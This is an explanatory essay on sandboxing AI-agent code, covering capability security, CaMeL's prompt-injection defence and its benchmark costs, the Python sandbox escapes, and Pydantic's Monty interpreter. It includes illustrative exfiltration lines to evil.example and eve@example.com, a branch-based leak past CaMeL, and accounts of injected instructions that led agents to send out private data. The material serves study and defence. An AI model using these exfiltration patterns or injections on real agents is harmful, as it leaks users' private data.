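A sceptic could object that these designs only rename I/O. If a host carries out every request, a program that returns `WriteFile "both.txt"` has the same effect as one that writes the file itself. Ordinary programs also have to go through the kernel to use the disk. Rigo describes the new PyPy sandbox as using basically the same security approach as an operating system.

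The objection holds for a host that carries out every request, because such a host adds no safety. But a host can also apply rules specific to this program, which the kernel normally doesn't. The kernel checks whether the shop owner's account may write to `both.txt`, and the account usually may. The host receives each request before anything happens, so it can refuse by returning `RequestFailed`, write the text to a temporary folder instead, record the request, or wait until the owner approves it. If the host has no code for a certain kind of request, the program can't perform that action.

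Developers can also test such a program without real files. They can pass made-up responses to `main` and check which requests it returns, or reproduce a failure by saving the responses from the failed run and passing them to `main` again.

But the host usually can't inspect all of the program's actions in advance. In the `IO` version of the sales program, everything after the first `>>=` is a function that produces the next action only when it receives Monday's sales. The host has to decide whether to allow the first read before it can check what the program will do with the text.

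Sending requests to a host also takes time, because the program has to stop at each one. The delay can be short within a single process. OCaml's runtime, for example, suspends and resumes code quickly because it doesn't copy the stack. PyPy's requests pass between two processes, so a program that makes many small reads needs many round trips. A host can reduce the number of trips by offering larger operations, such as reading a whole file at once.

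The two processes also have to convert the data they exchange. PyPy's sandbox converts each function's name and arguments into bytes, and the controller converts them back. Some objects, such as open files, can't be converted this way, so the controller sends a number in place of an open file.

A program can make only the requests that the host's developers foresaw. In the old PyPy sandbox, calling `os.readlink` to find where a symbolic link points crashes the controller and ends the program. By contrast, Willison (2026) reports in *pydantic-monty investigation* that unsupported features in Monty generally produce clean errors.

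Somebody also has to write the host's side of every operation. HaskellWiki's *The I/O problem* quotes the computer scientist William Stoye's complaint that embedding a functional language in a conventional one often moves much of the programming work into the conventional language. Stoye considered this a defeat for functional languages, but it is less of one in a sandbox, where the host's developers would want to write the code that accesses files and networks anyway.

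## Giving code only the powers it needs

A host that receives every request still has to decide what each program may do. In the capability approach, code starts with no powers and can use only those it receives. The text `"notes.txt"` only names a file, so code that has the text still needs separate permission to open the file. An open file object is a capability because it both identifies the file and lets any code that holds it use the file. The host decides on access once, when it passes the object.

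### Variable scope as a barrier

In 1996, Jonathan Rees argued that ordinary programming languages already contain most of what this approach needs. Code can use a variable only within the variable's scope, the part of a program where its name has a meaning. Rees designed W7, a security kernel (the core of a system that protects its resources). It consists of the lambda calculus, a minimal language of functions, with a few additions for changeable data, abstract data types and access to hardware.

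In Rees's example, Bart has written a program that sorts numbers and offers it to Lisa. She wants to sort a list of credit card numbers but fears that the program might secretly email them to Bart. She could run it on a computer with no network connection, but that is inconvenient and would also stop the program from fetching harmless information.

In W7, a function can use only its arguments and the values in its environment, the table that gives each name in the code its meaning. Suppose Lisa's system evaluates Bart's source code in an environment that contains arithmetic and list operations but no way to send email. If the code calls `send_email`, the name has no meaning there, so the system doesn't have to detect malicious code to stop it from sending email.

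A function keeps the environment in which it was created, even when somebody calls it from elsewhere. If Bart creates the sorting function in an environment of his own and gives Lisa the finished function, it can still use everything in that environment. It doesn't even need email to steal the numbers. Rees's version of the trick is in the language Scheme, but in Python it would look like this:

```python
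saved = []

def sort(numbers):
    saved.append(numbers)
    return sorted(numbers)
```

Lisa gets a correctly sorted list, and Bart later reads the card numbers from `saved`. The function performs no I/O at all.

Rees's remedy is a third person, Ned, whom both of them trust. Ned takes Bart's source code and rejects it if it contains any operation that changes a stored value. Otherwise, he evaluates it in a fresh environment and passes the function to Lisa. This test is crude, and a similar one for Python would reject the harmless `totals` function from the sales example because it changes a dictionary. Rees notes that every safe test must reject some harmless programs, since no test can decide in all cases whether a program might reveal its input. An agent's host has an easier job than Lisa because it receives source code and can create a new environment for each run.

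Rees also showed that people could do real work in such a system. Scheme 48, a complete version of Scheme built on W7, ran mobile robots at Cornell University without any other operating system and ran a secure multi-user system on ordinary workstations.

Scope protects a host only if the language has no way around it. Standard Python has one, as Chermside's open-file example on the Python Wiki shows. *LACUNA* (2026) applies Rees's idea to agents in Scala, a language with stricter rules. A model writes code to fill a gap in an existing program, and the variables in scope at the gap are the agent's permissions. If they include a read-only file but no network connection, the model's code can read the file but can't send its contents anywhere.

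### A square-root library that keeps a log

The Spritely Institute's Oaken project is developing a version of Scheme for running untrusted code, such as modifications to a game. Rees's work directly inspired it, and Rees advises the project. Preston-Kendal, in *Announcing Spritely Oaken*, introduces the design with a square-root library written by a colleague, Christine. Translated into Python, it looks roughly like this:

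```python
def square_root(x):
    log = open("sqrt-log.txt", "w")
    guess = 1.0
    while abs(guess * guess - x) >= 0.01:
        log.write(f"guess: {guess}\n")
        guess = (guess + x / guess) / 2
    return guess
```

The function improves its guess until the guess squared is within 0.01 of `x`. For the number 2, it logs the guesses 1.0 and 1.5 and returns about 1.417. Christine only wanted the log for debugging, but the function overwrites any file that already has the log's name. In Scheme, the library has to import the file operations to write the log, which would also let it read the user's private files.

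In the improved version, the caller supplies the logging function:

```python
def square_root(x, log):
    guess = 1.0
    while abs(guess * guess - x) >= 0.01:
        log(guess)
        guess = (guess + x / guess) / 2
    return guess
```

Christine can pass a function that writes each guess to a file, and somebody who doesn't want a log can pass one that does nothing. The library can still cause output, but only through the caller's function. If that function adds lines to one file, the library can't use it to read browser cookies. The Scheme version now imports only the base library, which contains no I/O, so a reviewer can check the list of imports instead of studying the algorithm.

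Every call then needs the logging function as an extra argument, much as a version of `totals` without I/O would need the exchange rate. Oaken instead lets a program pass the logging function once, when it imports the library. Standard Scheme has no way to do this for a whole library.

### Taming and attenuation

Security researchers call this kind of change taming. To tame a library is to use the features of the language to make it give less access than it originally did. A related technique is attenuation, which means passing on a power in a weaker form. If a host has a function that can send a message to any address, it can give the sandboxed code this one instead:

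```python
def message_owner(text):
    send_message("owner@example.com", text)
```

The code can now write to the owner and nobody else, provided that the language keeps it from getting at the original `send_message`.

Sometimes only the user knows which power the code needs. When a user uploads a file to a website, the browser shows a list of files, the user picks one, and the website receives an object that can read only that file. This is called the powerbox pattern. The user grants permission by choosing the file, without a separate security prompt.

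Preston-Kendal expected taming to be easy but found new problems almost every day. Confining a library to one folder is simple, for example, but the library can still fill the whole disk from there. Preventing this requires help from the operating system, so Preston-Kendal expected to leave that protection out of Oaken's first version. The announcement also has no finished design for network access, because loading a separate copy of a library for every server it contacts would be tedious. Processor time and memory need separate limits, since code can use them up without holding any capability.

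Repeated attenuation is also difficult. Suppose a program gives a library 100 megabytes of storage, and that library gives 10 of them to another library. The first library must put a tighter limit on storage functions that are already limited. Preston-Kendal was still looking for a convenient way to do this, and real programs need one because their libraries often depend on other libraries.

### Code Mode

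The internet company Cloudflare uses the capability approach for code written by AI agents. In its system, Code Mode, a model writes a JavaScript function that combines several operations. Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* explains that each run gets a new Dynamic Worker, an isolated environment that the host creates for it. The code has JavaScript's standard features but not the file and process functions that a server would normally add. Calls to `fetch()` and `connect()`, which would contact the network directly, fail by default.

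The code can act only through host functions, which Cloudflare groups into "connectors". With a GitHub connector, for example, the code can call `github.list_pull_requests()`. The connector, which runs outside the sandbox, contacts GitHub with the user's credentials and returns the data. The code never receives the credentials, so it can't leak them, though malicious code can still misuse the connector while running.

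A developer can require the user's approval for some functions. When the code calls one, the host records the call and stops the run. If the user approves, the host reruns the code from the beginning. It supplies the recorded results of earlier calls instead of repeating them, then performs the approved action and lets the code continue. An approval can therefore wait for days without the host keeping a half-finished program in memory. The method works only if the code makes the same calls in the same order each time, so code that depends on random numbers or the time has to record those values too.

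Cloudflare (2026) turns Code Mode on by default in its portals, which connect an agent to many services, but warns developers that "code execution does not replace authorization". Although the sandbox forces the code to use the connector, the connector's developer still has to check, for example, whether a user may delete a particular GitHub repository.

### How much one function should allow

The protection depends on how much each host function can do. These four hypothetical functions all let an agent communicate:

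| Host function | What the code can do with it |
|---|---|
| `post_to_team(text)` | Post messages in one chat room |
| `post(room, text)` | Post in any room that the account can use |
| `get(url)` | Read any web page |
| `request(method, url, body)` | Read or change data on any web service it can reach |

With `post_to_team`, the worst the code can do is post something false, annoying or confidential to the team, but the agent can't use it to answer a customer. With `request`, the agent can do almost any job on the web, but the host has given back most of the network access it removed. If the host is inside a company's network, the code may reach internal services that an outside attacker couldn't.

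The function `get` can leak data, because a web address can carry data. A call to `get("https://evil.example/?total=150")` sends Ada's total to the owner of that server. In *CapLite*, Xu, Liu and Nakayama (2026) tested an attack that tried to make agents fetch an attacker's address with a function meant only for reading. It succeeded in 85 of 168 attempts on agents without a special defence. The researchers' own system blocked every attempt, because it lets an agent visit only addresses that the user has stated.

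A short list of functions can still give code a lot of power. Cloudflare's *Code Mode* describes a server that gives agents the company's entire API, with more than 2,500 operations, through just two functions, one to search for operations and one to run code that uses them. According to Cloudflare, these operations cover domain names, stored data and programs on its servers. With this design, the model needs to read only about 1,000 tokens of descriptions, and the developers don't have to foresee every task. But the sandbox does little to limit the damage an agent can do, which depends on the user's credentials and the checks on each request.

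### How two harmless functions leak data

Narrow functions can also be dangerous in combination. Suppose the shop owner's agent can call `read_sales()`, which returns the sales table, and `send_message(address, text)`. Code that has only the first function can read private data but can't send it anywhere. Code that has only the second can send messages but knows nothing private. Code that has both can do this:

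```python
send_message("eve@example.com", read_sales())
```

Eve could cause this by placing an order with an instruction to the agent in the comment field. The code opens no files or connections itself, and the host allows each call it makes. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) makes the same criticism of permission rules and approval prompts, which can let an agent read a secret in one step and send it away in another.

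The host could prevent this leak by replacing `send_message` with `message_owner`. But the owner may want the agent to email every customer their total, and then the code needs both the sales data and the power to write to other people. A list of permitted functions can't allow the code to send Ada her total while forbidding it to send Eve the whole table. `send_message` can't distinguish the two cases either, because it receives two ordinary strings with no record of where they came from.

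### CaMeL

CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", keeps such a record. Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). CaMeL builds on the programmer Simon Willison's earlier proposal to divide an agent's work between two models. A privileged model reads the user's request and plans the work but never sees data from files, emails or web pages. A quarantined model reads that data but can't call any functions.

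Suppose the shop owner writes, "Tell Ada that her total is 150. Her address is in customers.txt." The privileged model turns the request into a short program, much like this:

```python
notes = read_file("customers.txt")
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find Ada's email address", notes)
send_message(address, "Your total is 150.")
```

An instruction that Eve hides in the file can't add another call, because the model that wrote the program never reads the file. But the file might falsely state that Ada's new address is `eve@example.com`, and the quarantined model might return that address. Willison (2025) acknowledges in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that the original two-model design had this flaw.

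CaMeL addresses the flaw with its own interpreter for a restricted version of Python. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and the people who may read it, and a value computed from others inherits their labels. `address` therefore carries the label of the untrusted file. Before each call, a policy written by the developers checks the labels of the arguments. A policy for `send_message` might allow known addresses and require the user's approval for any other. The labels also prevent the leak of the sales table to Eve, who isn't listed among its readers. CaMeL calls these labels capabilities, although they describe data and don't give code the power to use a resource.

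### What CaMeL costs in completed tasks

Much of the evidence comes from *AgentDojo*, a benchmark with 97 tasks, such as managing email or booking travel, and 629 security tests. Xu and colleagues used it to test 15 open-weight models, most of them small. Without a defence, the agents completed 59.4% of the tasks, and 2,322 of 13,935 attacks succeeded. With the CaMeL defence, they completed 24.9%, and 20 attacks succeeded. CaMeL also used more than three times as many tokens. Part of the drop in completed tasks came from models that couldn't write working programs. One model failed to produce a runnable program in 68% of its attempts.

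More capable models lose less performance under CaMeL. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (*Can CaMeLs Talk?*, 2026) ran teams of agents on industrial maintenance tasks, using CaMeL's two models and interpreter but no policies. Success fell by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Most of the failures arose because the privileged model has to write the whole program before any data has been read, so the program can't choose a new step when something unexpected turns up, as an ordinary agent can.

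Policies further reduce the share of tasks completed, even with capable models. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks. GPT-5.2 completed 66.7% of them without policies and 37.5% with them, while MiMo-v2.5 fell from 70.8% to 37.5%. Among the runs that finished, five of 622 attacks succeeded without policies and none of 588 with them. In *SecureClaw* (2026), an adapted version of CaMeL completed 29 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks and stopped all 629 attacks.

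Some of these losses don't come from poor design. Three of the 16 banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and act on its contents. One is to pay a bill, and an attacker who replaces the bill can make the agent pay the wrong person. The labels are the same whether or not the bill is genuine, so a policy has to block both payments or allow both unless it asks the user. But Willison worries that people who see too many approval requests will start to accept all of them, and that few users can write good policies.

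The two-model design provided most of the protection in the banking tests. The policies stopped the few remaining attacks but made the system much less useful. A host could reasonably reserve strict policies for functions that send money or private data.

### Gaps in the tracking

Data can influence what a program does without being copied into an argument. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen, while keeping up to 57% of the performance of leading models. The privileged model writes a program with many branches, such as closing a cookie notice if one appears. An attacker can't add a branch but can choose which one runs, for instance by making an advertisement look like a cookie notice so that the agent clicks on it.

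In the same way, a program can reveal a secret through the branches it takes. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL misses some of these leaks. This program is a variation on their example:

```python
large = True
small = True
if balance > 1000:
    small = False
if small:
    large = False
if large:
    send_message("eve@example.com", "large")
```

If the balance is 5,000, the program sets `small` to `False`, and CaMeL labels `small` as depending on the secret balance. The program then skips `large = False`, so CaMeL never labels `large`. The message appears to depend on nothing secret, so CaMeL allows it. If the balance is 500, no message goes out. Either way, Eve learns whether the balance exceeds 1,000. A privileged model that has read only the user's request is unlikely to write such a program, but a host can't rely on these labels when an attacker may have written the code. Garby and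 colleagues also found a simpler error that non-malicious code could trigger, in which inserting an untrusted value into a longer string makes it trusted.

The labels also disappear when one agent gives instructions to another. In an attack by Peters-Gill and colleagues on two agents running CaMeL, a database of job applicants contained a hidden instruction. The first agent summarized the database and put the summary into its request to the second, which treated the whole request as trusted and emailed the applicants' data to an outsider. Sending instructions and data separately, with the labels attached to the data, stopped every such attack in their tests.

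### Checking code before it runs

CaMeL checks each call when the program reaches it, so a program may do part of its work before the interpreter stops it. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) adds a check of the whole program before it starts. For example, the check can reject a program that would disconnect a computer from the network without first getting approval, and it returns to the model the path through the code that broke the rule. Because the check has to allow for any number of passes through a loop, it also rejects some safe programs.

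Odersky and colleagues use a compiler for a similar purpose. Their agents write code in a safe subset of Scala, and the type of each function records which capabilities it can use. Private data comes in a container that lets code apply only pure functions to its contents. The agent's code can count the words in a secret contract or compare it with another, but the compiler rejects any function that also holds a reference to a file or network connection. The result also stays in a container that the agent can't open.

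This method needs no plan written in advance, so an agent can look at ordinary data and then decide what to do next. Odersky and colleagues found no significant loss in task performance. But a malicious web page can still influence their agent, and the compiler will accept any harmful action the agent's capabilities allow.

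## Stripping an existing language or building one from nothing

A host that controls code through the functions it provides needs a language with no other way to reach files and networks. Such a language can be made by removing the dangerous parts of a full language, or by starting from nothing and adding only harmless parts. People have tried removing the dangerous parts of Python since the 1990s.

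### Python's restricted mode

Early versions of Python had a restricted mode and a module, `rexec`, that used it. Python's creator, van Rossum (2009), described the usual method on the developers' mailing list. The host runs untrusted code with a shortened table of built-in functions and replaces `import` with a version that loads only approved modules.

Python's `rexec` sandbox stopped working when the language introduced "new-style" classes, which gave code new ways to get from one object to another. Python's developers disabled `rexec` in version 2.3.

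In 2009, a programmer called Tav wanted to revive restricted mode. Tav blamed the failure of `rexec` on its use of classes and proposed relying on functions instead, much as Rees had done in W7. Ordinary Python code can inspect a function and read its private variables, which would defeat the plan, so Tav offered a six-line patch to close the last two such leaks Tav knew of. Another developer, Benjamin Peterson, doubted the fix would last, because new versions of Python would surely bring new ways around it.

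Van Rossum suggested building a sandbox and inviting people to break out of it. Tav published one called `safelite.py`, and people soon broke out of it.

### Three years of pysandbox

The Python developer Victor Stinner nevertheless thought Tav had found something interesting, and added more protections. Stinner describes what happened next in *The pysandbox project is broken* (2013).

Stinner released pysandbox 1.0 in June 2010 and used it in a chat bot on a French Python channel. The bot ran any code that people sent it, and most of its users were hackers trying to escape the sandbox.

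After three months, somebody found that sandboxed code could change the dictionary where Python keeps its built-in functions, and so tamper with the sandbox's own protections. Stinner wanted to use a special protected type there, but CPython accepted only an ordinary dictionary, so he had to block the operations that delete entries from every dictionary in the program. For example, a sandboxed program could no longer remove a customer from a table of totals with `del sums["Ada"]`. Somebody soon found another dictionary method with the same effect, and Stinner blocked that too.

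More vulnerabilities turned up seven months later. Stinner also gave up on the time limit, because it couldn't interrupt a long calculation inside a built-in function written in C. He blocked one attribute because code could use it to crash the interpreter, but he had to lift the block for Python 2.5 because of a different bug in that version.

In autumn 2013, attackers in a public security challenge found two flaws in pysandbox in less than a day. One let them extract the contents of files from the error messages of a built-in function unrelated to reading files. The other let them follow Python's record of an error back to the host's variables.

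Stinner fixed both and began a new version that ran the untrusted code in a separate process, but he had already concluded that the project was "broken by design". Its safety depended on all of CPython, which had more than 126,000 lines of C in two directories alone, and a single bug anywhere could be enough to let code escape. The protections had also made the sandbox nearly useless, because they all had to stay on and the host couldn't pass its own objects to the code. Stinner wrote that pysandbox "cannot be used in practice" for anything more complex than `1+(2*3)`.

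Stinner's sandbox failed at both safety and usefulness because many ordinary Python features can give a program access to files. Python lets a program inspect almost everything about itself, including the types of its objects, the variables of its functions and the chain of calls that led to the current line. Debuggers and testing tools depend on this. CPython's built-in functions also open files themselves, for example to quote a faulty line in an error message. Stinner had to find and block every feature that led back to a file, since an attacker needed only one that he had missed. Many of those features had ordinary uses, so blocking them also limited what legitimate programs could do.

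Developers of AI agents have since tried the same approach. The restricted Python executor in Hugging Face's agent library smolagents checked code before and during a run. Corgea's *smolagents has Sandbox Escape Vulnerability in the local_python_executor.py Module* reports that attackers could escape the executor in version 1.14.0 through modules and functions it explicitly allowed. The agent framework PraisonAI blocked a list of dangerous attribute names, but GitLab's *GHSA-pv2j-rghr-v5r9* (2026) describes how code could read all of those attributes through a text-formatting feature.

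### Java's Security Manager

Java kept its I/O operations and had the Security Manager check each one before it ran. The Security Manager was part of Java from version 1.0 and was first used to restrict applets, small programs that web browsers downloaded and ran. Java's class libraries had only eight core packages then, and *JEP 411* (2021), OpenJDK's proposal to phase out the Security Manager, says this small size made the checks feasible.

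Later versions extended the checks to all code, and the libraries kept growing. *JEP 486* (Mullan and Buckley, 2024) counts over 1,000 methods that had to check for permission and over 1,200 that had to claim extra permissions for themselves. For example, Java's date library had to read a time-zone file even when the program calling it was not allowed to read files. Every change to one of these methods needed a security review.

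OpenJDK's official reasons for removing the Security Manager are mostly this cost and how few people benefited. A developer who only wanted to limit file reading to one folder also had to list permissions for everything else the program did. Because the Security Manager checked all the code that led to an operation, an application usually needed every permission its libraries needed. In Mullan and Buckley's experience, most of the few applications that turned it on granted all permissions. The checks were also slow, and they did not address 19 of the 25 most dangerous software weaknesses on a 2020 industry list.

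Java 24 permanently disabled the Security Manager in 2025. Mullan and Buckley advise sandboxing Java programs from outside, with containers, virtual machines or operating system features. Stinner had already recommended the same approach for Python, putting the whole process in an external sandbox, such as one that filters its system calls.

### Lua, a language small enough to strip

Lua shows that stripping can work much better when the language is small. Developers embed Lua in games and servers so that users can write scripts. Its functions for files and for running other programs are in separate libraries, `io` and `os`. The host program chooses which libraries to load, and the rest of the language works without these two.

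The host still has to remove parts of Lua's standard library. The basic library includes two functions that run code from files and another that accepts precompiled code, which can crash the interpreter if maliciously crafted. The `debug` library can break a script's isolation, and the `package` library can load other modules. But one person can review this list in an afternoon, which nobody could do for CPython.

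Even a short list can go wrong. The database Redis lets its users run Lua scripts without I/O. In 2022, Debian's version of Redis was found to have left Lua's module loader accessible, so scripts could load libraries that Redis had meant to leave out. In 2025, the security company Wiz disclosed an error in how Redis's copy of Lua frees memory, which had been there for about 13 years. A script could use the error to run any code on the server, even with `io` and `os` left out.

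### Monty

Pydantic took the second approach with Monty, an interpreter its developers wrote in Rust. In the launch article, Pydantic compares locking down a full system to a game of whack-a-mole and proposes to "start from nothing" instead.

According to Pydantic's *Security Model*, Monty doesn't have to block access to files or the network, because "the interpreter implements no such operation". The clock and the source of random numbers are exceptions, and the host can replace both. The host can share objects as well as functions and folders. It wraps each object and lists the attributes and methods the code may use, so the code could be allowed to call `withdraw` on a bank account but not `close`. Stinner never found a way to pass arbitrary objects into pysandbox safely.

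Because Monty stops at every call to a host function, the host can save the whole program at that point. Suppose an agent writes this code, in which all three functions belong to the host:

```python
bill = make_bill("Ada")
if ask_owner(bill):
    send_bill(bill)
```

When the program pauses at `ask_owner`, the host can save it, including the value of `bill`, to a file of a few kilobytes and shut everything down. When the shop owner answers the next day, the host loads the file, perhaps on another machine, and passes in the answer as the result of `ask_owner`. Unlike Cloudflare's Code Mode, Monty doesn't have to rerun the code from the beginning. But Monty doesn't check whether somebody has altered the saved file, so the host has to keep that file safe.

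Code without I/O still needs limits on memory and time. Pydantic's *Resource Limits* describes how the host can limit the memory for each session and the running time for each piece of code in Monty. Both limits are off by default. The expression `'x' * 10**12` would need about a terabyte, but if a memory limit is set, Monty calculates the size in advance and raises an error without trying to create the string.

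The running time doesn't include time spent waiting for the host, so a slow database can't use it up. Code could exploit this by calling host functions in an endless loop, so Monty allows only 1,000 exchanges with the host per session by default. A long built-in operation can also overrun the time limit, because Monty checks the clock only at certain points. Stinner's time limit had the same weakness. Monty runs code in a separate worker process, so the host can kill it when a deadline passes. After code exceeds a memory or time limit, the host should discard the session, since its data may be damaged.

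Willison had Anthropic's Claude Code examine Monty in May 2026 and reported that the limits on time, memory and recursion "all appear to work as advertised". This supports the documentation, but such a brief investigation can't rule out an escape from the sandbox.

### How much Python Monty supports

Monty has grown quickly and is no longer experimental. Pydantic (2026) lists version 1.7.0, released on November 24, 2026, as stable. Monty aims to behave like CPython 3.14 wherever it supports a feature at all. Pydantic's *Limitations* gives the current state:

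| Part of Python | Supported | Missing |
|---|---|---|
| Functions | Nested and asynchronous functions, decorators | Generator functions (`yield`) |
| Classes | Simple classes, data classes | Properties, class methods, new exception types |
| Statements | Loops, `try`, `with`, `match` | `del` |
| Standard library | Parts of about 30 modules, including `json`, `csv`, `re`, `datetime` and `statistics` | `enum`, `string`, `logging`, `uuid`, `socket`, `subprocess` |
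| Third-party packages | None | All |

Pydantic left out `socket` and `subprocess` on purpose, because they would open the sandbox. It simply hasn't written some of the other modules yet.

Neither Monty nor pysandbox lets a program run `del sums["Ada"]`. Stinner had to forbid it in pysandbox because attackers could use it to reach what he was hiding. Monty's interpreter contains no hidden file functions, so Pydantic could add `del` without giving code a new route to the disk.

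A missing language feature also matters less when a model writes the code. In *Running Pydantic's Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly*, Willison (2026) tried an early version of Monty that lacked classes and didn't think this was a problem for its intended use. A model that gets an error message about classes can rewrite the code without them. Each attempt takes time and tokens, though, and a model can't replace a sizable missing library by rewriting its code.

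This only works if there is an error message. In a few cases, Monty runs the code without an error but does something different from CPython. For example, a programmer can define an empty shopping cart to count as false. Monty ignores that definition, so the code after `if cart:` runs even when the cart is empty. Pydantic documents these differences, but a model trained on ordinary Python won't account for them.

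### What the start-up times are worth

Pydantic's *Comparison to Alternatives* measured how long different sandboxes take to start and to run ten short commands. Pyodide is CPython compiled to WebAssembly, mainly for use in browsers, and wasmtime runs a similar build of CPython outside the browser.

| Sandbox | Start and run `1 + 1` | Run ten commands once started |
|---|---|---|
| Monty | 0.8 ms | 0.4 ms |
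| CPython in wasmtime | 16 ms | 180 ms |
| Docker container | 195 ms | 700 ms |
| Pyodide | 2,700 ms | 35 ms |

Pydantic, which makes Monty, produced these figures itself, and its method favours Monty somewhat. It had already started Monty's worker processes before it began timing, while the other sandboxes started from nothing. If Monty has to start its workers first, the time rises to 5 milliseconds. The setups for the other sandboxes also didn't keep variables from one command to the next, so they had to rerun all the earlier commands each time. Monty would still be much faster than Docker without these advantages.

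Pydantic's launch figure of 0.004 milliseconds dates from when Monty ran inside the host's process. Monty now runs in a separate worker process, which adds some time, but a crash in the sandbox no longer brings down the host.

For a single agent, the difference hardly matters. In Pydantic's weather comparison, writing code saved 3.1 seconds, nearly all of it by making fewer calls to the model. A Docker container would have added back about 0.2 seconds, whereas starting Pyodide would have added back 2.7. Monty's speed and size matter more to a company that runs short scripts for many users at once. Each worker needs about 2 megabytes plus whatever memory the host allows the code, so one machine can run hundreds.

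### The first escape from Monty

In spring 2026, Pydantic offered $5,000 to anyone who could read a secret from a server running Monty. Owen Kwan of the security firm Veria Labs did so in less than 48 hours. Hewitt (2026) reports in *Hack Monty* almost 1.5 million requests from about 650 internet addresses.

The secret was in an environment variable, and Monty had no operation for reading one. Kwan got it through a memory error. Rust normally prevents such errors, but its checks make it awkward to write an interpreter in which many objects refer to one another. Pydantic had therefore written a few parts of Monty in "unsafe" Rust, which leaves some of those checks to the programmer. Those parts relied on Monty's garbage collector, which frees memory no longer in use, but it sometimes freed an object that the program was still using. An attacker could exploit this to take control of the interpreter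 and run code that wasn't Python. The 2025 flaw in Redis's copy of Lua was of the same general kind.

Pydantic fixed the error and held a second round from the end of May. Pydantic's *Hack Monty Round 3 & Round 2 results* reports that nobody escaped, and announces a third round in August with a bounty of up to $20,000. Hewitt credits the design for there being only one escape in more than a million requests in the first round. The number of requests is weak evidence, since many may have tried the same things, but one serious flaw and a second round without an escape is still a much better record than pysandbox's.

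Pydantic also reduced the damage a future escape could do. The worker processes start with no environment variables, so a secret like the one Kwan read would no longer be there. But a worker still runs with the application's operating-system privileges, so code that escaped from Monty into its worker could read any file the application can read, unless the host adds a container or another outer barrier. Pydantic sells a server version that includes such a barrier.

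### Choosing between the two

The two approaches differ most in what happens when a developer overlooks a feature of Python. If Stinner overlooked one, an attacker could use it to escape. If Pydantic overlooks one, a program stops with an error or occasionally gives a wrong result, and somebody files a bug report. New versions of Python add to the work of stripping the language, because each new feature might give code access to files again, whereas Pydantic can ignore a new feature until it wants to support it.

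Monty, which was built from nothing, lacks Python's third-party packages and much of its standard library. Pysandbox stripped Python instead, but it also failed to keep existing programs working, which is the apparent advantage of stripping. By the end of the project, sandboxed programs couldn't rely on basic dictionary operations.

A third option is to leave the language alone and remove I/O underneath it, as the PyPy sandbox and CPython in wasmtime do. In Pydantic's comparison, that build of CPython supports almost all of the language and many packages, but it can't open a network connection or start a program. Pydantic's whack-a-mole argument is weaker here. It fits pysandbox well, but Pydantic aims it at containers and virtual machines, the kind of outside barrier that Stinner and the Java developers came to recommend. Those barriers control the few routes by which a process can reach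 anything else, so they don't have to deal with each of Python's features separately.

An outside barrier can have gaps too. The tool `mcp-run-python` ran Python in Pyodide but, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-25905* (2026), left open a bridge from the Python code to the surrounding JavaScript environment. Code could use the bridge to take over the server, although WebAssembly itself had worked as intended.

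Monty may also lose some of its advantage as it grows. Pydantic names Prefect and Hugging Face among the companies that already use Monty to run agents' code, and their models will keep writing code that needs more of Python's features. Each addition makes the interpreter larger, and an error in any part that handles memory directly could again let code escape the sandbox.

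## What still gets in and out when I/O is removed

The escapes from pysandbox and Monty depended on mistakes in the sandboxes. But even a sandbox without mistakes lets some information through, because the code runs on a real computer and somebody uses its result.

Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, gave this difficulty its name. A customer passes private data to a program that somebody else wrote, and wants to be sure that the program can't send the data to its owner. Lisa has this problem when she gives her card numbers to Bart's sorting program. Lampson found three kinds of channel through which data can escape:

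- Storage channels are places that the program can write to and another program can read, such as files.
- Legitimate channels are outputs that the program is supposed to produce, such as the bill for its services, since the owner gets a copy.
- Covert channels aren't meant for communication at all. For example, the program can alternate between heavy and light work, and another program on the same computer can notice the changes in speed.

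Removing I/O closes most storage channels. The host also has to start each run from a clean state, so that a program can't keep data for its owner the way Bart's program did with `saved`.

Lampson estimated that a bill in a fixed format can still carry a few bits or tens of bits. To close the channel completely, the customer would have to set the amount in advance, as with a purchase order. To close covert channels, the system would have to make the program's visible behaviour match the customer's specification, perhaps by slowing it down. Lampson expected this to take a lot of resources and suggested limiting the leak instead, which would take fewer. Steven Lipner agreed in 1975. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, he thought closing covert channels would carry a "direct and unreasonable performance penalty".

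### Noninterference

Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, introduced a way to define a program that leaks nothing, known as noninterference. Let P be a program with a secret input s and a public input p. In its simplest form, noninterference means that for every p and any two secrets s1 and s2:

```
what an observer sees of P(s1, p) = what the observer sees of P(s2, p)
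```

The observer can't learn anything about the secret, because every possible secret looks the same.

Suppose the shop owner's program emails Ada her total. Ada is the observer, her own purchases are the public input, and everyone else's are secret. If Ben had spent 500 instead of 75, the total in Ada's email would still be 150, so the email's text reveals nothing about his purchases.

Besides the text of the email, Ada may learn something from when it arrives and whether it arrives at all. `totals` takes longer to process a longer table, so the arrival time could in principle reveal how many sales the shop made. If one of Ben's amounts is a word instead of a number, `totals` stops with an error and Ada gets no email.

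Whether this program satisfies noninterference therefore depends on what Ada can observe. Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) point out in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* that this is true of any system. For example, a smart card's electricity use matters because an attacker may control the terminal that powers the card.

A host can't establish noninterference by watching a single run, since the definition compares runs with different secrets. The host needs a proof about the whole program. Garby and colleagues used the proof checker Lean to prove a version of noninterference for every program in a small language for AI agents, including agents that generate and run code. Their version allows for the randomness of a model's answers, but it doesn't cover leaks that depend on whether a program finishes.

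### How many bits a small leak carries

If an observer sees only whether a program finishes, each run reveals at most one bit, the answer to one yes-or-no question. For example, malicious code could loop forever if the shop's balance exceeds 1,000. One bit is often harmless, but 20 runs with a different question each time can identify one number among about a million.

The one-bit limit also assumes that the program produces no output while it runs. *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (Askarov, Hunt and colleagues) describes a program that prints 0, 1, 2 and so on, and gets stuck when it reaches the secret number. The last number printed is the secret, yet the leading tools for checking information flow accepted such programs as secure.

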